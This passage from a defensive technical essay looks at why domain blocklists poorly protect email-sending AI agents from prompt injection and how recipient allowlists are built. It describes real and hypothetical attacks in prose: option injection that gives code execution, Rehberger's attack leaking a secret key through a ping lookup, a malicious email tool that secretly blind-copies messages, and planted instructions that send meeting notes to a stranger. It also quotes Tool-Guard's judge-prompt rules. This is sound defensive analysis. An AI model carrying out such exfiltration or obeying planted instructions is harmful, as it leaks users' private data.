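Escaping a value too early can be as unsafe as not escaping it, because later decoding can introduce new HTML characters. Joomla, a system for running websites, escaped users' email addresses and then decoded any Punycode in them with a faulty library that could produce such characters. Heyes used this to put styling code on a page that administrators view, and from there ran commands on the server. Joomla fixed the fault in February 2024.

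Stripping means deleting the unwanted characters and using what remains. GitHub's *Validate all the things* (2022) calls this kind of repair the least effective technique, though better than nothing. Its example is a program that tries to confine file names to one folder by deleting every `../`, the notation for a parent folder. An attacker can put one `../` inside another, so that deleting the inner one leaves the outer one intact. It would be safer to work out the file's full path and reject it if it is outside the folder.

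Silently repairing a destination argument is especially risky because the result may be a working address that the user never chose. Nodemailer in effect made such a repair when it deleted a comment and thereby created the attacker's domain. Poh found a milder case in Jakarta Mail, which removes spaces from malformed newsgroup names although, according to a note in its code, it should report an error. By contrast, Larson (2026), in *[CVE-2026-1299] email BytesGenerator header injection due to unquoted newlines*, announced that Python's corrected email module rejects badly formed headers.

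A program can safely make changes that don't alter what a value means, such as putting a domain in lower case or removing spaces at the end of a subject. If it would have to guess what a value was supposed to be, it should refuse the value. A refused value can also be evidence of an attack. MDN advises website owners to watch for input that no ordinary user could have entered, since it strongly suggests a deliberate attack. A line break in a recipient's address deserves similar attention, and the application could reasonably log it and stop the task without giving the model another try.

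### Values that become command options

Escaping is often unnecessary if a program passes values separately from the command, as parameterised queries do for databases. Operating systems let one program start another with a list of arguments, without using a shell (the software that interprets typed command lines). Characters that a shell would interpret then have no special effect.

This is not enough for agents that run command-line programs. *Prompt injection to RCE in AI agents*, published by the security firm Trail of Bits in October 2025, described attacks on three popular agents. The firm could not name them because disclosure was still under way. The agents ran certain commands without asking the user because the commands seemed safe. In each agent, a single prompt let the testers run code of their choice.

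The attacks used command options, which usually begin with a hyphen and appear in the same list as ordinary values. One agent could run a project's tests with any options, including one that runs another program. The developers of another agent had blocked several well-known dangerous options, but the testers found two permitted commands with unrestricted options. They used one command to write a file and the other to run it.

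The remaining agent's search tool built the command with its own code, which put the model's search term straight into the argument list. The search program therefore treated a term that began with a hyphen as an option. Putting a double hyphen, `--`, before the term fixes this, because the program then treats everything after it as an ordinary value. Mail tools can have the same problem. The `PLAIN` pattern lets an address begin with a hyphen, which is harmless if the tool uses a mail library, but a command-line mail program could treat the address as an option.

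The separator does not help when the model is supposed to choose the options, as in the test-running agent. A narrower tool could take only the name of a test and let the application's code supply the options. Trail of Bits recommends a sandbox as the main defence. This is an isolated environment that limits which files and network connections a command can reach. If a sandbox is impossible, Trail of Bits prefers tools with their own checking code to a list of supposedly safe commands.

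The testers typed their prompts directly but report that the same prompts work when planted in code comments or repositories. They give no success rates, so the study shows that these attacks are possible but not how often they succeed.

Trail of Bits considers it impractical to filter dangerous options one by one, because common utilities have hundreds of options and some are dangerous only in combination. Such a filter is a blocklist, and its author would have to know every option of every permitted program and keep up with each new version.

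## How domain blocklists are made and how late they list a domain

Security companies, industry groups and volunteers maintain blocklists of domains seen in attacks, and mail providers, browsers and network operators use these lists to protect billions of people. An application can look up attacker.test in the same lists before it sends the stranger a copy of the meeting notes, but this only helps if the domain is already listed. Researchers have measured how long blocklists take to list phishing domains, which criminals use with fake messages and websites to steal passwords or money.

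### Where the entries come from

A domain usually gets onto a list after somebody has seen it in an attack. The Anti-Phishing Working Group (APWG), an industry association, collects reports from member companies, research partners and the public, according to its *Phishing Activity Trends Reports*. List operators also run spam traps, which are addresses that no person uses, so any mail they receive is unsolicited. Crawlers visit suspicious web pages and check whether the pages imitate a bank or a login screen.

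The consulting firm Interisle uses blocklists to study the market for domain names. Its June 2026 report, *Submission of Interisle research report* (Rose and Aaron, 2026), explains that two large list operators, Spamhaus and SURBL, find some domains by examining what spam messages advertise. When an operator has found one bad domain, it can look for others bought from the same registrar (a company that sells domain names) at about the same time and pointed to the same servers.

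Spamhaus' *Frequently asked questions* describes its Domain Blocklist as a list of domains with poor reputation. Spamhaus calculates reputation from many factors, so such a list can include a domain that nobody has reported. Some criminals leave new domains unused for months because such scoring systems rate young domains as less trustworthy.

### Querying a list

Many lists answer queries through DNS. The program puts the domain in front of the list's own name and looks up the result as if it were an ordinary domain:

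```
lookup:   attacker.test.<name of the list>

answer:   no such name (NXDOMAIN)     not listed
          127.0.x.x                   listed
          127.255.255.x               query error (Spamhaus)
```

Operators differ in how they use these answers. Abusix, another list operator, treats any address that begins with 127 as a listing (*Query Basics*). Spamhaus counts only those that begin with 127.0 (*DQS Requests*) and reserves the 127.255.255 range for query errors (Spamhaus, 2019). A program that applied Abusix's rule to Spamhaus would read every such error as a listing and could refuse every recipient. A lookup that times out gives no answer, so the developer has to decide what happens then. For a tool that sends email, it is safer to ask the user than to assume that the domain is clean.

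Spamhaus intends its domain list for the domains in email addresses as well as those in links. The office assistant's application should therefore normalise the domain of every recipient and every link in the body, then look it up in the list. The list's operator can learn from these queries which domains the company writes to. A company that objects to this can use a downloadable list and search it locally.

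### Kinds of list

The most familiar blocklists cover phishing and malware. Some cover one type of attack, such as PhishTank for phishing and URLhaus for malware, and others cover several. Some list full web addresses because criminals also put pages on free hosting services, where blocking the whole domain would also block honest customers' pages. *Cybercrime Supply Chain Studies* (2026), the Cybercrime Information Center's summary of Interisle's annual research, counts over 1.1 million hostnames at such services that were used in the latest year's attacks, 67% more than the year before.

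Disposable-mail lists contain the domains of services that give anyone a temporary mailbox. Websites use them to reject throwaway accounts. Few employees have a business reason to write to such a mailbox, so an agent's application can refuse these domains without blocking much legitimate email. But the lists don't cover a domain that an attacker has bought for an attack.

Lists of newly registered domains include domains without any evidence of an attack. Their makers often start from the daily files of registered names available from ICANN, which oversees generic endings such as .com. Sommese, Akiwate and colleagues (2024), in *DarkDNS*, tried to find new domains sooner by watching the public logs of website certificates, which browsers use to confirm that they have reached the right domain. Of the domains they found over three months, they detected half within 45 minutes of registration.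 But they found only 42% of all new domains before the daily files included them, because the rest did not get a certificate immediately. A domain that only receives stolen email needs no website, so it may never get a certificate.

An attacker can also wait until a domain is no longer new. Rose and Aaron report that between June and December 2025, blocklists added 2.32 million domains registered in 2024, at least five months earlier. A rule that refuses domains less than 30 days old would have let all of these through by the time they were listed, but it would refuse a new client whose company had just set up its domain.

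An organisation can also keep its own list of addresses seen in attacks on its staff. The list can include individual mailboxes, which helps against an attacker who reuses an account at a large mail provider. It would not have helped with the October invoice fraud, because the recipient's address was at the target's own company.

### How long listing takes

In *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration*, Lim, Mok and colleagues (2025) studied 690,502 phishing domains from seven lists over 39 months, up to October 2024. They first separated domains that criminals had registered for phishing from legitimate sites that criminals had broken into. They classified a domain as maliciously registered if it contained a brand name or a variation of one, contained no English word, or belonged to a batch of similar names bought together. These criteria put 66.1% of the domains in that group, and the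 rest counted as compromised.

The researchers found registration dates for 76.3% of the domains. The median time from registration to listing was 16.3 days for maliciously registered domains and 86 days for compromised ones. The averages were far higher, at 206.4 and 332.1 days, because some domains took more than a year. The median also varied with the brand the criminals imitated, from 1.4 days for the US Postal Service to 52.5 for Facebook and 440.4 for Microsoft.

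All these delays are measured from the day of registration, which may be long before the first attack. If a criminal leaves a domain unused for two months and a list adds it on the day of the first attack, the measured delay is two months, although the list was hardly late. The delay from first use is probably much shorter, but it can still be too long. Sommese and colleagues cite a 2020 study in which the average phishing campaign took 21 hours from its start to its last victim.

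The median of 86 days for compromised domains is surprisingly short, because an honest owner has usually had a domain for a long time before anyone breaks into the site. Interisle treats any domain listed within 90 days of registration as malicious, since it is usually too new for anyone to have compromised it. By that rule, more than half of the "compromised" domains with known dates were malicious ones that the researchers' tests missed. The 66.1% malicious share may therefore be too low, although the test for English words could also have wrongly labelled some honest firms with foreign names as malicious. Interisle's own estimate, in *Phishing Landscape 2026* (Strutt and Piscitello, 2026), is higher, at about three quarters of phishing domains in recent years.

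Domains that APWG had already listed took a median of 2.3 more days to appear on PhishStats, 3.7 on Malware-filter, 4.1 on OpenPhish, 4.4 on PhishTank, 64.4 on Phishing.Database and 930.8 on phishunt.io. But Lim and colleagues collected APWG's list from July 2021 and the others only from 31 May 2024, so a domain that phishunt.io had listed in 2022 could appear to have been added two years late. The delays of a few days are more believable, and even those are longer than many phishing campaigns last.

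A listing doesn't disable the domain. Lim and colleagues found that phishing domains stayed in the DNS for an average of 11.5 days after detection. Rose and Aaron found much slower removal for .loan domains. Only 7.2% of the 76,892 listed .loan domains were removed before they were a year old. An attacker can therefore keep receiving mail at a listed domain from any agent whose application doesn't check the list.

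### How little the lists overlap

Rose and Aaron counted the domains that eight lists added during 2025:

| List | What it covers | Domains listed in 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| Spamhaus Domain Blocklist | phishing, malware, spam and other abuse | 9,773,569 |
| SURBL | phishing, malware and other abuse | 6,536,604 |
| APWG | phishing | 207,812 |
| Invaluement | risky domains in spam messages | 183,107 |
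| PhishTank | phishing | 100,097 |
| OpenPhish | phishing | 95,412 |
| Malware Patrol | malware and the control of infected computers | 17,042 |
| URLhaus | malware | 11,503 |
| All eight, without duplicates | | 14,855,456 |

The eight counts add up to 16,925,146, about 2.07 million more than the number of distinct domains. At most about 2.07 million domains were therefore on more than one list, so at least 86% were on just one. Spamhaus, the largest list, had about two thirds of the distinct domains. A developer who queried only PhishTank would have covered less than 1% of them.

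Plonka, Palacio and Perouli (2025), in *Is Protective DNS Blocking the Wild West?*, found a similar pattern in three free lists. Protective DNS is a service that withholds the correct answer when a user looks up a listed domain. The researchers compared a phishing and scam list from Open Threat Exchange, a general threat list by a curator called HaGeZi and a malware list from a university in Toulouse. Only 665 names were on all three:

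| Lists compared | Names in common |
|---|---|
| Open Threat Exchange and HaGeZi | 2,009 |
| Open Threat Exchange and Toulouse | 1,670 |
| HaGeZi and Toulouse | 55,451 |
| All three | 665 |

They then checked a week of real lookups from June 2025 on a network that serves hundreds of research and educational institutions. Of the 1.79 million different names looked up, 27 were on the Open Threat Exchange list, 2,907 on HaGeZi's and 236 on the Toulouse list. HaGeZi's list shared 27 of these names with the Toulouse list and 3 with Open Threat Exchange. The Toulouse and Open Threat Exchange lists had none in common.

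Curators disagree about what a threat is, so little overlap between their lists doesn't prove that each list missed what the others found. Plonka and colleagues mention a frequently visited domain that one curator blocks and another takes care not to block. A developer who combines several lists will catch more attacks but will also accept every curator's mistakes and choices. Rose and Aaron consider false listings rare on the eight lists they use, all of which have a way to correct such errors.

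### Malicious domains that no list includes

The study by Lim and colleagues included only domains that were on a blocklist, so its delays don't cover domains that are never listed. The best evidence on those comes from lists of domains that investigators compiled in another way. In May 2025, the FBI published more than 332,000 domains that it had found on the network of Funnull, a company that provided infrastructure for investment scams. Only 56.6% of them appeared on the blocklists that Interisle monitors, either before or after the FBI published them, which leaves about 144,000 unlisted. Funnull spread its registrations over many registrars and domain endings, so its domains may have been harder to find than most.

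In *Detecting Malicious Domain Registration Batches*, ICANN researchers Cheadle, Gañán and colleagues started from listed domains and searched for others registered in the same batches. Rose and Aaron report that the search found two unlisted domains for every three listed ones. Interisle found much worse cases. In one set of .pink domains that criminals used to imitate the messaging service Telegram, blocklists had included 6 domains and missed 176.

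Rose and Aaron used the ICANN ratio to estimate the total for 2025. Buyers registered 85 million domains under generic endings that year, and lists had included 8.5 million of them, or 10%, by 18 May 2026. Interisle expects this to reach 10.1 million by the end of 2026, as criminals begin to use domains they have held back. Adding two unlisted domains for every three listed ones gives

$$10.1 \text{ million} \times \left(1 + \tfrac{2}{3}\right) \approx 16.8 \text{ million}$$

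or about 20% of the year's registrations. On this estimate, lists will miss about 6.7 million malicious domains, which is 40% of the total.

The estimate assumes that the unlisted domains in a batch are malicious and that the ratio holds for the whole market. ICANN staff argue that such estimates depend on the definition of abuse, the standard of evidence and the method, according to CircleID, a website about internet infrastructure. But the ICANN study left out many batches, including those of more than 1,000 domains, and its researchers thought the true rate was probably higher. The 40% is rough, but it is close to the 43% that lists missed in the FBI's data.

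### Cheap domains in bulk

Criminals use far more domains than they did two years ago. Interisle's annual studies count the domains used in malware, phishing and spam attacks, and the 2025 figures are also in Interisle's *Cybercrime Supply Chain 2025* (2025):

| Study | Domains used in attacks | Of these, registered in bulk |
|---|---|---|
| 2024 | 8.6 million | 2.6 million |
| 2025 | 19.5 million | 7.3 million |
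| 2026 | nearly 24 million | 11 million |

Phishing alone accounted for 3.1 million domains in the year to April 2026, about twice as many as the year before, according to Cybercrime Information Center's *Phishing Activity*. Criminals had registered 74% of them for phishing. Its quarterly edition for May to July 2026 shows another 1.13 million, 81% of them registered maliciously.

Interisle counts blocklisted domains as registered in bulk if at least ten came from the same registrar, with no more than ten minutes between one registration and the next. Rose and Aaron report that 88% of the domains registered in 2025 and later blocklisted were registered in bulk. The largest batch had 10,848 domains, all registered at one Japanese company in a little over five hours.

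Most of these domains cost very little. *INFERMAL* (Nosyk, Korczyński and colleagues, 2025) matched 14,474 maliciously registered phishing domains with the prices registrars advertised on the day of registration. The prices ranged from $0.78 to $69, and nearly half were $2 or less. Rose and Aaron found some domains on sale in 2026 for as little as $0.49.

Nosyk and colleagues also compared combinations of registrar and domain ending. Each dollar off the price was associated with 49% more malicious registrations. Registrars that let programs create accounts or register domains automatically had 401% more, while strict registration rules were associated with 63% fewer. These are correlations, and the sample included only domains that were blocklisted within 90 days of registration and then taken down. The results therefore provide little evidence about criminals who wait before using their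 domains or whose domains nobody reports.

Some administrators respond by blocking every domain with a cheap ending. In Interisle's data, blocklists had listed 34.6% of the .top domains registered in 2025, compared with 4.9% of the .com domains. But .com had more malicious registrations than any other generic ending, at 1.93 million. Blocking .top would stop none of those, and it would also block many .top domains that were on no blocklist.

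### From phishing to agents

No published study seems to have measured how soon blocklists add domains that attackers use against AI agents. The phishing figures probably apply to campaigns that send the same prompt-injection email to thousands of companies, because some copies will reach spam traps or people who report them, and a list operator can then extract the attacker's domain from the text.

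An attack on one company's assistant gives blocklist operators much less evidence than ordinary phishing does. The attacker sends one email and needs one domain that can receive mail. There may be no web page for a crawler to visit, and the user may never see the instruction or learn about the blind copy. If the attacker buys only one domain, operators can't link it to others bought in the same batch. Sommese and colleagues cite earlier research in which blocklists generally missed spammers' domains until the spammers had used them and someone had reported them. A domain that nobody reports is therefore likely to be listed later than an ordinary phishing domain, or never.

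A late listing is also less useful here than for a phishing site, where it still protects later visitors. If a list adds attacker.test two days after the assistant sent the meeting notes there, the stranger already has them. The application can still log the domains it sends mail to and query the lists again some weeks later. If one of those domains had been listed since, the company would know to investigate an email that seemed harmless when the assistant sent it.

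## Why blocklists of addresses and domains are a weak defence

Even if blocklists were faster and more complete, an attacker could still get past them, because they let through every destination that isn't listed and the attacker chooses the destination. A new address or domain costs very little, and the attacker needs only one that passes. These claims hold for most attacks on an agent that sends email, though each has limits.

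### How far the argument holds

A blocklist allows every destination it doesn't list. Omissions are also harder to notice than on an allowlist, where leaving out a client makes the user's email fail and somebody complains. When a blocklist omits an attacker, the email goes out and nobody has a reason to investigate.

The attacker can usually choose the destination, because planted text can contain any address. The October invoice fraud was an exception, since the email had to reach the target's own accounts-payable staff.

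New domains are cheap, as registrars' prices show, but some other destinations are harder to obtain. An agent that pays invoices sends money to a bank account, and opening one under a false name takes more effort than buying a domain. A list of known fraudulent accounts is therefore harder to evade than a list of domains, though organised criminals can still do it. APWG's *Phishing Activity Trends Report, 2nd Quarter 2026* (2026) describes a gang, Scripted Sparrow, that controls a vast network of accounts for receiving stolen money, most of them at US banks.

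A blocklist that works well for a mail provider can be a poor defence for an agent. If a mail provider's list stops 90% of phishing emails, it prevents roughly 90% of the damage, because each email threatens a different person. When an agent holds a secret, the first leak causes most of the damage, and blocking later attempts doesn't undo it.

### The arithmetic

Suppose that a list catches a share $c$ of fresh domains, and that each domain's chance is independent of the others. If an attacker tries $n$ domains, the probability that at least one passes is

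$$P = 1 - c^n$$

If a list catches 90% of an attacker's domains, the chance that at least one gets through is $1 - 0.9^{10} \approx 0.65$ after ten tries and about 0.90 after 22. The table also shows a weaker and a stronger list, with each domain priced at $2.

| Share of fresh domains caught | At least one of 10 passes | At least one of 22 passes | Domains needed for a 90% chance | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
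| 60% | 99% | over 99.9% | 5 | $10 |
| 90% | 65% | 90% | 22 | $44 |
| 99% | 10% | 20% | 230 | $460 |

The 60% row matches Interisle's rough estimate that blocklists eventually catch about 60% of malicious domains. They probably catch a smaller share of domains on their first day of use.

The formula assumes that the agent always follows the planted instruction. In controlled trials by Wu and colleagues, specially designed emails succeeded 73.54% of the time. At that rate, an attacker facing the 90% list needs 31 tries, instead of 22, to have a 90% chance of succeeding at least once.

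The assumption that domains are listed independently is more doubtful. A list operator that recognises one domain from a batch may list the whole batch, so ten domains bought together may be little more use to an attacker than one. The attacker can avoid this by buying them from different registrars. Criminals as a group already use many registrars. In APWG's figures for email fraud against businesses, the most popular, NameCheap, accounted for only 16% of the domains.

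An attacker's odds also depend on how the check handles a call that includes a listed recipient. The send_email schema allows eleven recipients per call. If the check removes listed recipients and sends the email to the rest, an attacker can try eleven domains in one call, with a 69% chance that at least one passes the 90% list. If the check refuses the whole call when any recipient is listed, adding addresses only makes a refusal more likely.

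A refusal also gives the company an opportunity to respond. With the 90% list, an attacker has only a 10% chance of getting through before the first refusal. If that refusal stops the agent and leads someone to the planted email, the attacker may never get to try other domains. If nobody reads the log, the attacker can keep trying domains until one passes.

However, anyone can query a public blocklist, so an attacker can avoid most refusals by checking domains before using them. If a list catches 90% of new domains, the attacker has to buy ten on average, for about $20, to find one that isn't listed. The attacker then needs to send only one email, which the list will stop only if its operator adds the domain first. A private list prevents this lookup, but its operator still has to identify a domain that may never have been used in an attack.

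If the allowlist contains only example.com and the check compares whole domains correctly, a newly registered domain has no chance of passing, so $P$ is zero however many domains the attacker registers. The attacker would need control of a mailbox at example.com.

### Webmail, shared files and forms

An organisation can't block a domain that it needs for its own work. Many private customers and small firms use free webmail, so blocking a large webmail provider would cut them off along with the attacker. File-sharing and form services cause the same problem for agents that can open or submit web pages. All customers of such a service may share one domain, with only the rest of the web address to tell them apart:

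```
https://forms.example.net/f/staff-survey    the company's own form
https://forms.example.net/f/7kq2x           the attacker's form
```

A check on the domain treats an attacker's form and a legitimate form on the same domain alike. A blocklist of full web addresses could include the attacker's form after somebody reports it, but the attacker can then create another, often for free.

Criminals already use hosting providers that few organisations could block. In APWG's breakdown of phishing sites by hosting provider for the second quarter of 2026, Cloudflare had 34%, Amazon 11%, Microsoft 7% and Google 3%, or 55% in total. Some of these sites have their own domains, which a blocklist can include. But a company that blocked the providers would lose access to many legitimate sites, and probably to some of its own software.

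Listing individual webmail addresses doesn't work well either, because accounts are about as cheap as domains. Many online services send a code to a phone number before they open an account, but people sell these verifications. The University of Cambridge's *Price of a bot army revealed across hundreds of online platforms*, which covers more than 500 platforms, reports that a verification cost $0.26 on average in the US and $0.10 in the UK in the year to July 2025. When the researchers tried to verify US Facebook accounts, one large seller's service worked only 21% of the time, so each account would take about five purchases, while another's worked over 90% of the time. Ready-made accounts are also for sale. DomainTools' report *SecuritySnack* describes a shop with Gmail accounts from about $1.37.

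A single account can also have many addresses. If a provider ignores dots in the local part, the name "stranger" has seven places for a dot, so it has $2^7 = 128$ spellings, and tags after a plus sign add practically unlimited variants. The check can remove dots and tags before it compares an address with a blocklist. If the provider treats the spellings as separate mailboxes, the worst result is a false refusal. Removing dots and tags does not help the check catch a new account, however.

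Shared services are a problem for allowlists too, since permitting the domain permits every account on it.

### Models that recognise suspicious addresses

A language model can judge an address it has never seen, but it can have the same weakness as a fixed list if it refuses only the destinations it recognises as bad.

In 2025, the security researcher Johann Rehberger found a way to make Claude Code leak secrets. His article *Claude Code*, on his blog Embrace The Red, explains that the agent could run several network commands, including `ping`, without asking the user. Text planted in a source file could make the agent read a secret key and put it into a domain name. When the command looked up that name, it sent the key to the attacker's server. Rehberger reported the flaw on 26 May, and Anthropic had fixed it by 6 June.

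During Rehberger's tests, Claude refused to contact well-known services that security testers use to record incoming requests, such as oast.me and Burp Collaborator. When he switched to a domain not associated with security testing, the attack worked. He attributes the refusals to Claude's training. He doesn't report how many times he tried each domain, so it is unclear how consistent this behaviour was.

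The model was in effect applying a blocklist, since it refused the names it had learned and accepted an unfamiliar one. A developer can't inspect or add to such a list. Newer models may recognise more names, but training can't teach a model about a domain that somebody registers afterwards.

This case also shows that allowlists can fail. The commands ran without approval because they were on a list of safe commands. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-55284* (2025), an entry in a Spanish vulnerability database, calls that list "overly broad". Rehberger proposed removing `ping` and three similar commands from it, so that the user would have to approve them for any domain.

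Tool-Guard, a defence from *Think Twice Before You Act* (Shi, Wang and colleagues, 2026), has a similar weakness in how it checks arguments. It is designed to stop attackers who plant instructions in the descriptions of an agent's tools. Before a call runs, a language model judges whether the tool fits the task and whether the arguments look suspicious. The prompt names acceptable sources for a value, such as the user's request, and instructs the model to flag email addresses and bank accounts with "attacker-like patterns". It also sets the default answer to "not suspicious" and includes the instruction "Only flag if parameters contain clear attacker patterns." An address without such a pattern should therefore pass, even if the model can't identify its source.

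Shi and colleagues tested the defence on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated banking, chat, travel and office tasks. With GPT-4o as the agent's model, attacks succeeded in 43.30% of 97 tasks without the defence and in 2.06% (two tasks) with it. The rate was also 2.06% for a version that kept the checks but dropped the system's other main component, so the checks accounted for the reduction.

But the attackers in these tests used obviously malicious identifiers, such as the account number EVIL123456789 and a chat channel called #leaked-data. Shi and colleagues also tried attacks that adapted to the defence, and at most 2.06% succeeded. These attacks reworded the poisoned tool descriptions, but the paper's example still uses EVIL123456789. In another test, they reversed the default, so that the model had to treat arguments as suspicious unless it had grounds to accept them. The attack success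 rate stayed near zero. The reversed default ought to be safer, but a test with such obvious identifiers can't measure how much safer.

Real attackers can use ordinary domain names. In September 2025, the security firm Koi reported that postmark-mcp, an unofficial email tool for agents, was secretly sending a blind copy of every message to an address at giftshop.club. The domain displayed a marketplace for Paris-themed gifts, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails*. The tool's own code added the copy after the agent had made its call, so no check on the arguments could have caught it. But an attacker could also plant an address like this in an email, and a model looking for addresses that resemble an attacker's would have little reason to flag it.

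Tool-Guard also prompts the model not to treat a recipient as suspicious if it appears in earlier tool results. This is reasonable for the attack that Shi and colleagues studied, because the checks never receive the poisoned descriptions as evidence. But it would be a serious mistake for the office assistant, because the stranger's email is a tool result that contains the stranger's address.

### Older lessons about lists of bad input

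Web developers met the same problem when they tried to keep malicious scripts out of text that users post. Christey (2006), in *Blacklist defenses as a breeding ground for vulnerability variants*, describes an imaginary product whose vendor starts by removing script tags. The attacker then hides a script in an image's address. The vendor blocks that, and the attacker disguises the forbidden word by encoding a letter or splitting the word over two lines. Each patch leads to another variant, until the seventh patch permits only a few tags and attributes. Christey wrote this after the researcher David Litchfield repeatedly found ways around Oracle's attempts to fix one of its products.

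Christey worked at MITRE, a US non-profit that maintains a catalogue of software weaknesses. *CWE-184*, the catalogue's entry for incomplete lists of disallowed inputs, notes that developers may use such lists as a quick fix and that the lists often cover only the best-known bad inputs. Claude's refusal of well-known testing services fits that description. One of the entry's examples is an AI agent platform whose list missed an unusual way of writing a file path, which allowed attackers to run commands.

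Extending a list after every attack also takes a lot of work. *The disadvantages of a blacklist-based approach to input validation* (Dunn, 2018), a paper from the security company NCC Group, describes applications whose developers did this for years. One application replaced round and curly brackets with square ones, which enabled an attack that used square brackets. Dunn presumes that all this work took many times longer than writing a single allowlist check would have. He also warns that developers who wrongly believe their code is secure may be worse off than those who know it has problems.

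Scripts are hard to block mainly because the same attack can take many forms. For domains, normalisation deals with much of this variation, but it can't help with entirely new domains. Escaping can also make dangerous script text harmless without a list, whereas nothing similar can make an attacker's address safe to send to.

Another argument against blocklists is that there are usually far more bad things to list than good ones. Tech for Nonprofits' *The Six Dumbest Ideas in Computer Security* (2005) quotes the security specialist Marcus Ranum, who called this approach "Enumerating Badness". A typical antivirus program then knew of more than 75,000 viruses, while Ranum had installed about 30 legitimate programs, which would have been much easier to list. The imbalance is probably greater for email, since eight blocklists added 14.9 million domains in 2025 and an office worker may write to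 a few hundred domains in a year. The comparison does not work for an agent whose job is to write to people the company has never dealt with.

### Reasons to keep a blocklist

MITRE advises using lists of bad input only to detect suspicious activity, and domain blocklists work well for this. An agent doing legitimate work should almost never try to email a domain known for phishing. If it does, the application should stop the task and save everything the agent had read, so that someone can find the planted text. The same text may have reached other employees' agents, perhaps with a domain that isn't on the list.

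A blocklist is also quick to run, with one lookup per domain. By comparison, Tool-Guard's checks and repeated planning made tasks take about 3.7 times as long in tests with GPT-4o-mini.

Some attackers reuse domains, especially if they send the same planted instruction to thousands of companies. A blocklist may then protect later victims, though not the first ones. Having to replace domains and servers can also slow criminals down. In its report on the first quarter of 2026, Microsoft said that Tycoon2FA, a phishing service, had changed its hosting providers and its pattern of domain registration after a disruption, but had only partly recovered. This is indirect evidence at best, since disrupting a whole service does more than blocklisting its domains.

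In the postmark-mcp case, knowing the domain that received the stolen emails could help users find past leaks, but blocking it would probably not have stopped new ones. The developer deleted the package from the public registry, but versions already installed could keep sending copies of emails to giftshop.club. Koi published the domain and advised users to search their mail logs for it. The tool added the copies after any check on the agent's arguments, and Koi warns that such tools also bypass company email gateways. The only sure way to stop the copying was to remove the tool.

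A company with an allowlist can still use a blocklist to check the domains it permits. If criminals break into a supplier's site and its domain appears on a blocklist, the application can hold messages to that supplier until someone investigates.

For some agents, a blocklist may be the only practical list. An assistant that answers sales enquiries has to write to people at domains the company has never seen. CodePath's *Prefer whitelisting over blacklisting*, a guide for programmers, recommends a blocklist only when the legitimate values are open-ended, as they are here. The developer should assume that some messages will go to attackers and limit what those messages can contain. For example, the assistant could answer strangers from published product information, with no access to the mailbox or internal files. An attacker who takes control of it through an email can still make it send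 embarrassing or fraudulent messages, but it has no private documents to attach.

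## Building an allowlist of recipients and domains

Nylas, which sells software for connecting programs to mailboxes, says most internal agents write to fewer than 20 addresses, though it gives no data. An allowlist that short is easy to write, but many developers never write one. Microsoft (2026) lists agents that choose their email recipients at runtime among ten common misconfigurations. It says people often add an email action for testing or notifications and leave the recipient field unrestricted.

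An allowlist can be as narrow as one address fixed in code or as broad as several whole domains. The table lists the rules roughly from tightest to loosest.

| Rule | Where it fits | Legitimate email it blocks |
|---|---|---|
| Code fixes the recipient | alerts, reports and notes to the user | email to anyone else |
| The model picks a person from a directory | assistants for internal mail | email to people not yet in the directory |
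| Exact addresses | a few regular correspondents | email to a client's new employee |
| People in the thread being answered | replies | new conversations, or bringing in a colleague |
| One domain per session | an enquiry to one outside company | email to a company's second domain |
| Whole domains | staff who write to many people at a few firms | a first email to a new client |

Several of the following examples come from vendors' pages. They show how companies build these rules, but none includes a test of how well the rules stop attacks.

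### Fixed recipients and directory identifiers

An agent that reports only to its own user doesn't need a recipient argument. The application can offer a tool such as `email_me(subject, body)` and take the address from the user's login. A planted instruction can then change the message's contents but not its recipient. Zapier's *Decide if AI should guess the value of a specific field* describes a similar setting for tools that people set up without programming. Users can fix a field's value or leave out an optional field such as Bcc, and the model can't override either choice.

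The mail service can also enforce the limit. Cloudflare's *Configure send bindings* describes a setting that restricts a program's mail connection to a single destination address. This restriction holds even if the application's own check has a bug.

With a fixed recipient, the office assistant would send the meeting notes to the user, who would have to forward them to Dana. Saving a draft for the user to send has much the same effect. Considus' *Prompt injection, where each Proton Bridge MCP defence stops* (2026), a developer's account of a mail tool for agents, describes a mode in which the assistant can file mail and write drafts but has none of the five tools for sending. The developer prefers this to refusing calls, because a model can be argued out of refusing. That is a good reason not to rely on the model to refuse, but it doesn't apply when code refuses the call. Removing the tool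 does also prevent pointless attempts to use it.

If the agent has to choose between recipients, the model can supply an identifier instead of an address:

```
send_email(to = ["emp-0412"], ...)    code looks up emp-0412
                                      and finds dana@example.com
```

The model can choose a recipient from a fixed set of identifiers, which the program maps to real addresses, rejecting anything else. MITRE calls this "enforcement by conversion". Because the model never writes an address, an attacker can't exploit lookalike domains or disagreements between mail parsers. The agent also can't hide an encryption key in the address, since choosing one of 500 employees conveys at most nine bits, and the recipient is a colleague.

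When the application looks up a recipient, it should search only the people this user's agent may write to. Y-Security's *Insecure Direct Object Reference Prevention Cheat Sheet* similarly advises web applications to look for a requested project among the current user's projects, not among all projects. Outsiders also must not be able to add entries to the directory. Some mail programs save every correspondent as a contact, so a stranger could get into the address book by sending one email. If the company employs two people called Dana, the application should show the user each person's name and department and let the user choose.

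### Exact addresses

An allowlist of exact addresses can include people outside the company, even those who use a large webmail provider. The office assistant could write to one client's webmail account without being able to write to everyone else's. Such a list would also have stopped the October invoice emails from reaching accounts payable, unless that department's address was on it.

Cloudflare offers a setting for this kind of list too. Maester's *AI agents should not send email with AI-controlled inputs*, a configuration test for Microsoft's systems, recommends a fixed list that neither user input nor generated text can change. These lists need a lot of upkeep, because people change jobs and the system refuses email to each new contact at a client until someone adds the address.

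### The people in the thread

When an agent answers an email, the application can take the recipients from that email and let the model write only the body. Nylas recommends allowing only the original message's sender and reply-to address. Text planted in the message then can't add a recipient. But the rule's safety depends on who chose the thread and who is in it.

If the allowlist includes the participants in an email thread, the user should choose the thread, for example by opening a message and asking for a reply. If the model can choose, a stranger can send an email that instructs it to reply with meeting notes attached, and the allowlist will permit the reply because the stranger is a legitimate participant in that thread.

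The sender also controls most of an email's headers, so the addresses in the Reply-To and Cc fields can belong to anybody. It is safer to reply only to the sender's address, once the mail server has authenticated it, and to check any other address in the thread against a separate list.

Considus' mail tool uses a looser version of this rule. It permits any address that has appeared in the header of an email, and refuses addresses that have appeared only in body text or attachments. This would stop the agent from forwarding invoices to an address mentioned only in an email's text, but the stranger in the running example could get around it by sending the first email from stranger@attacker.test or copying that address in.

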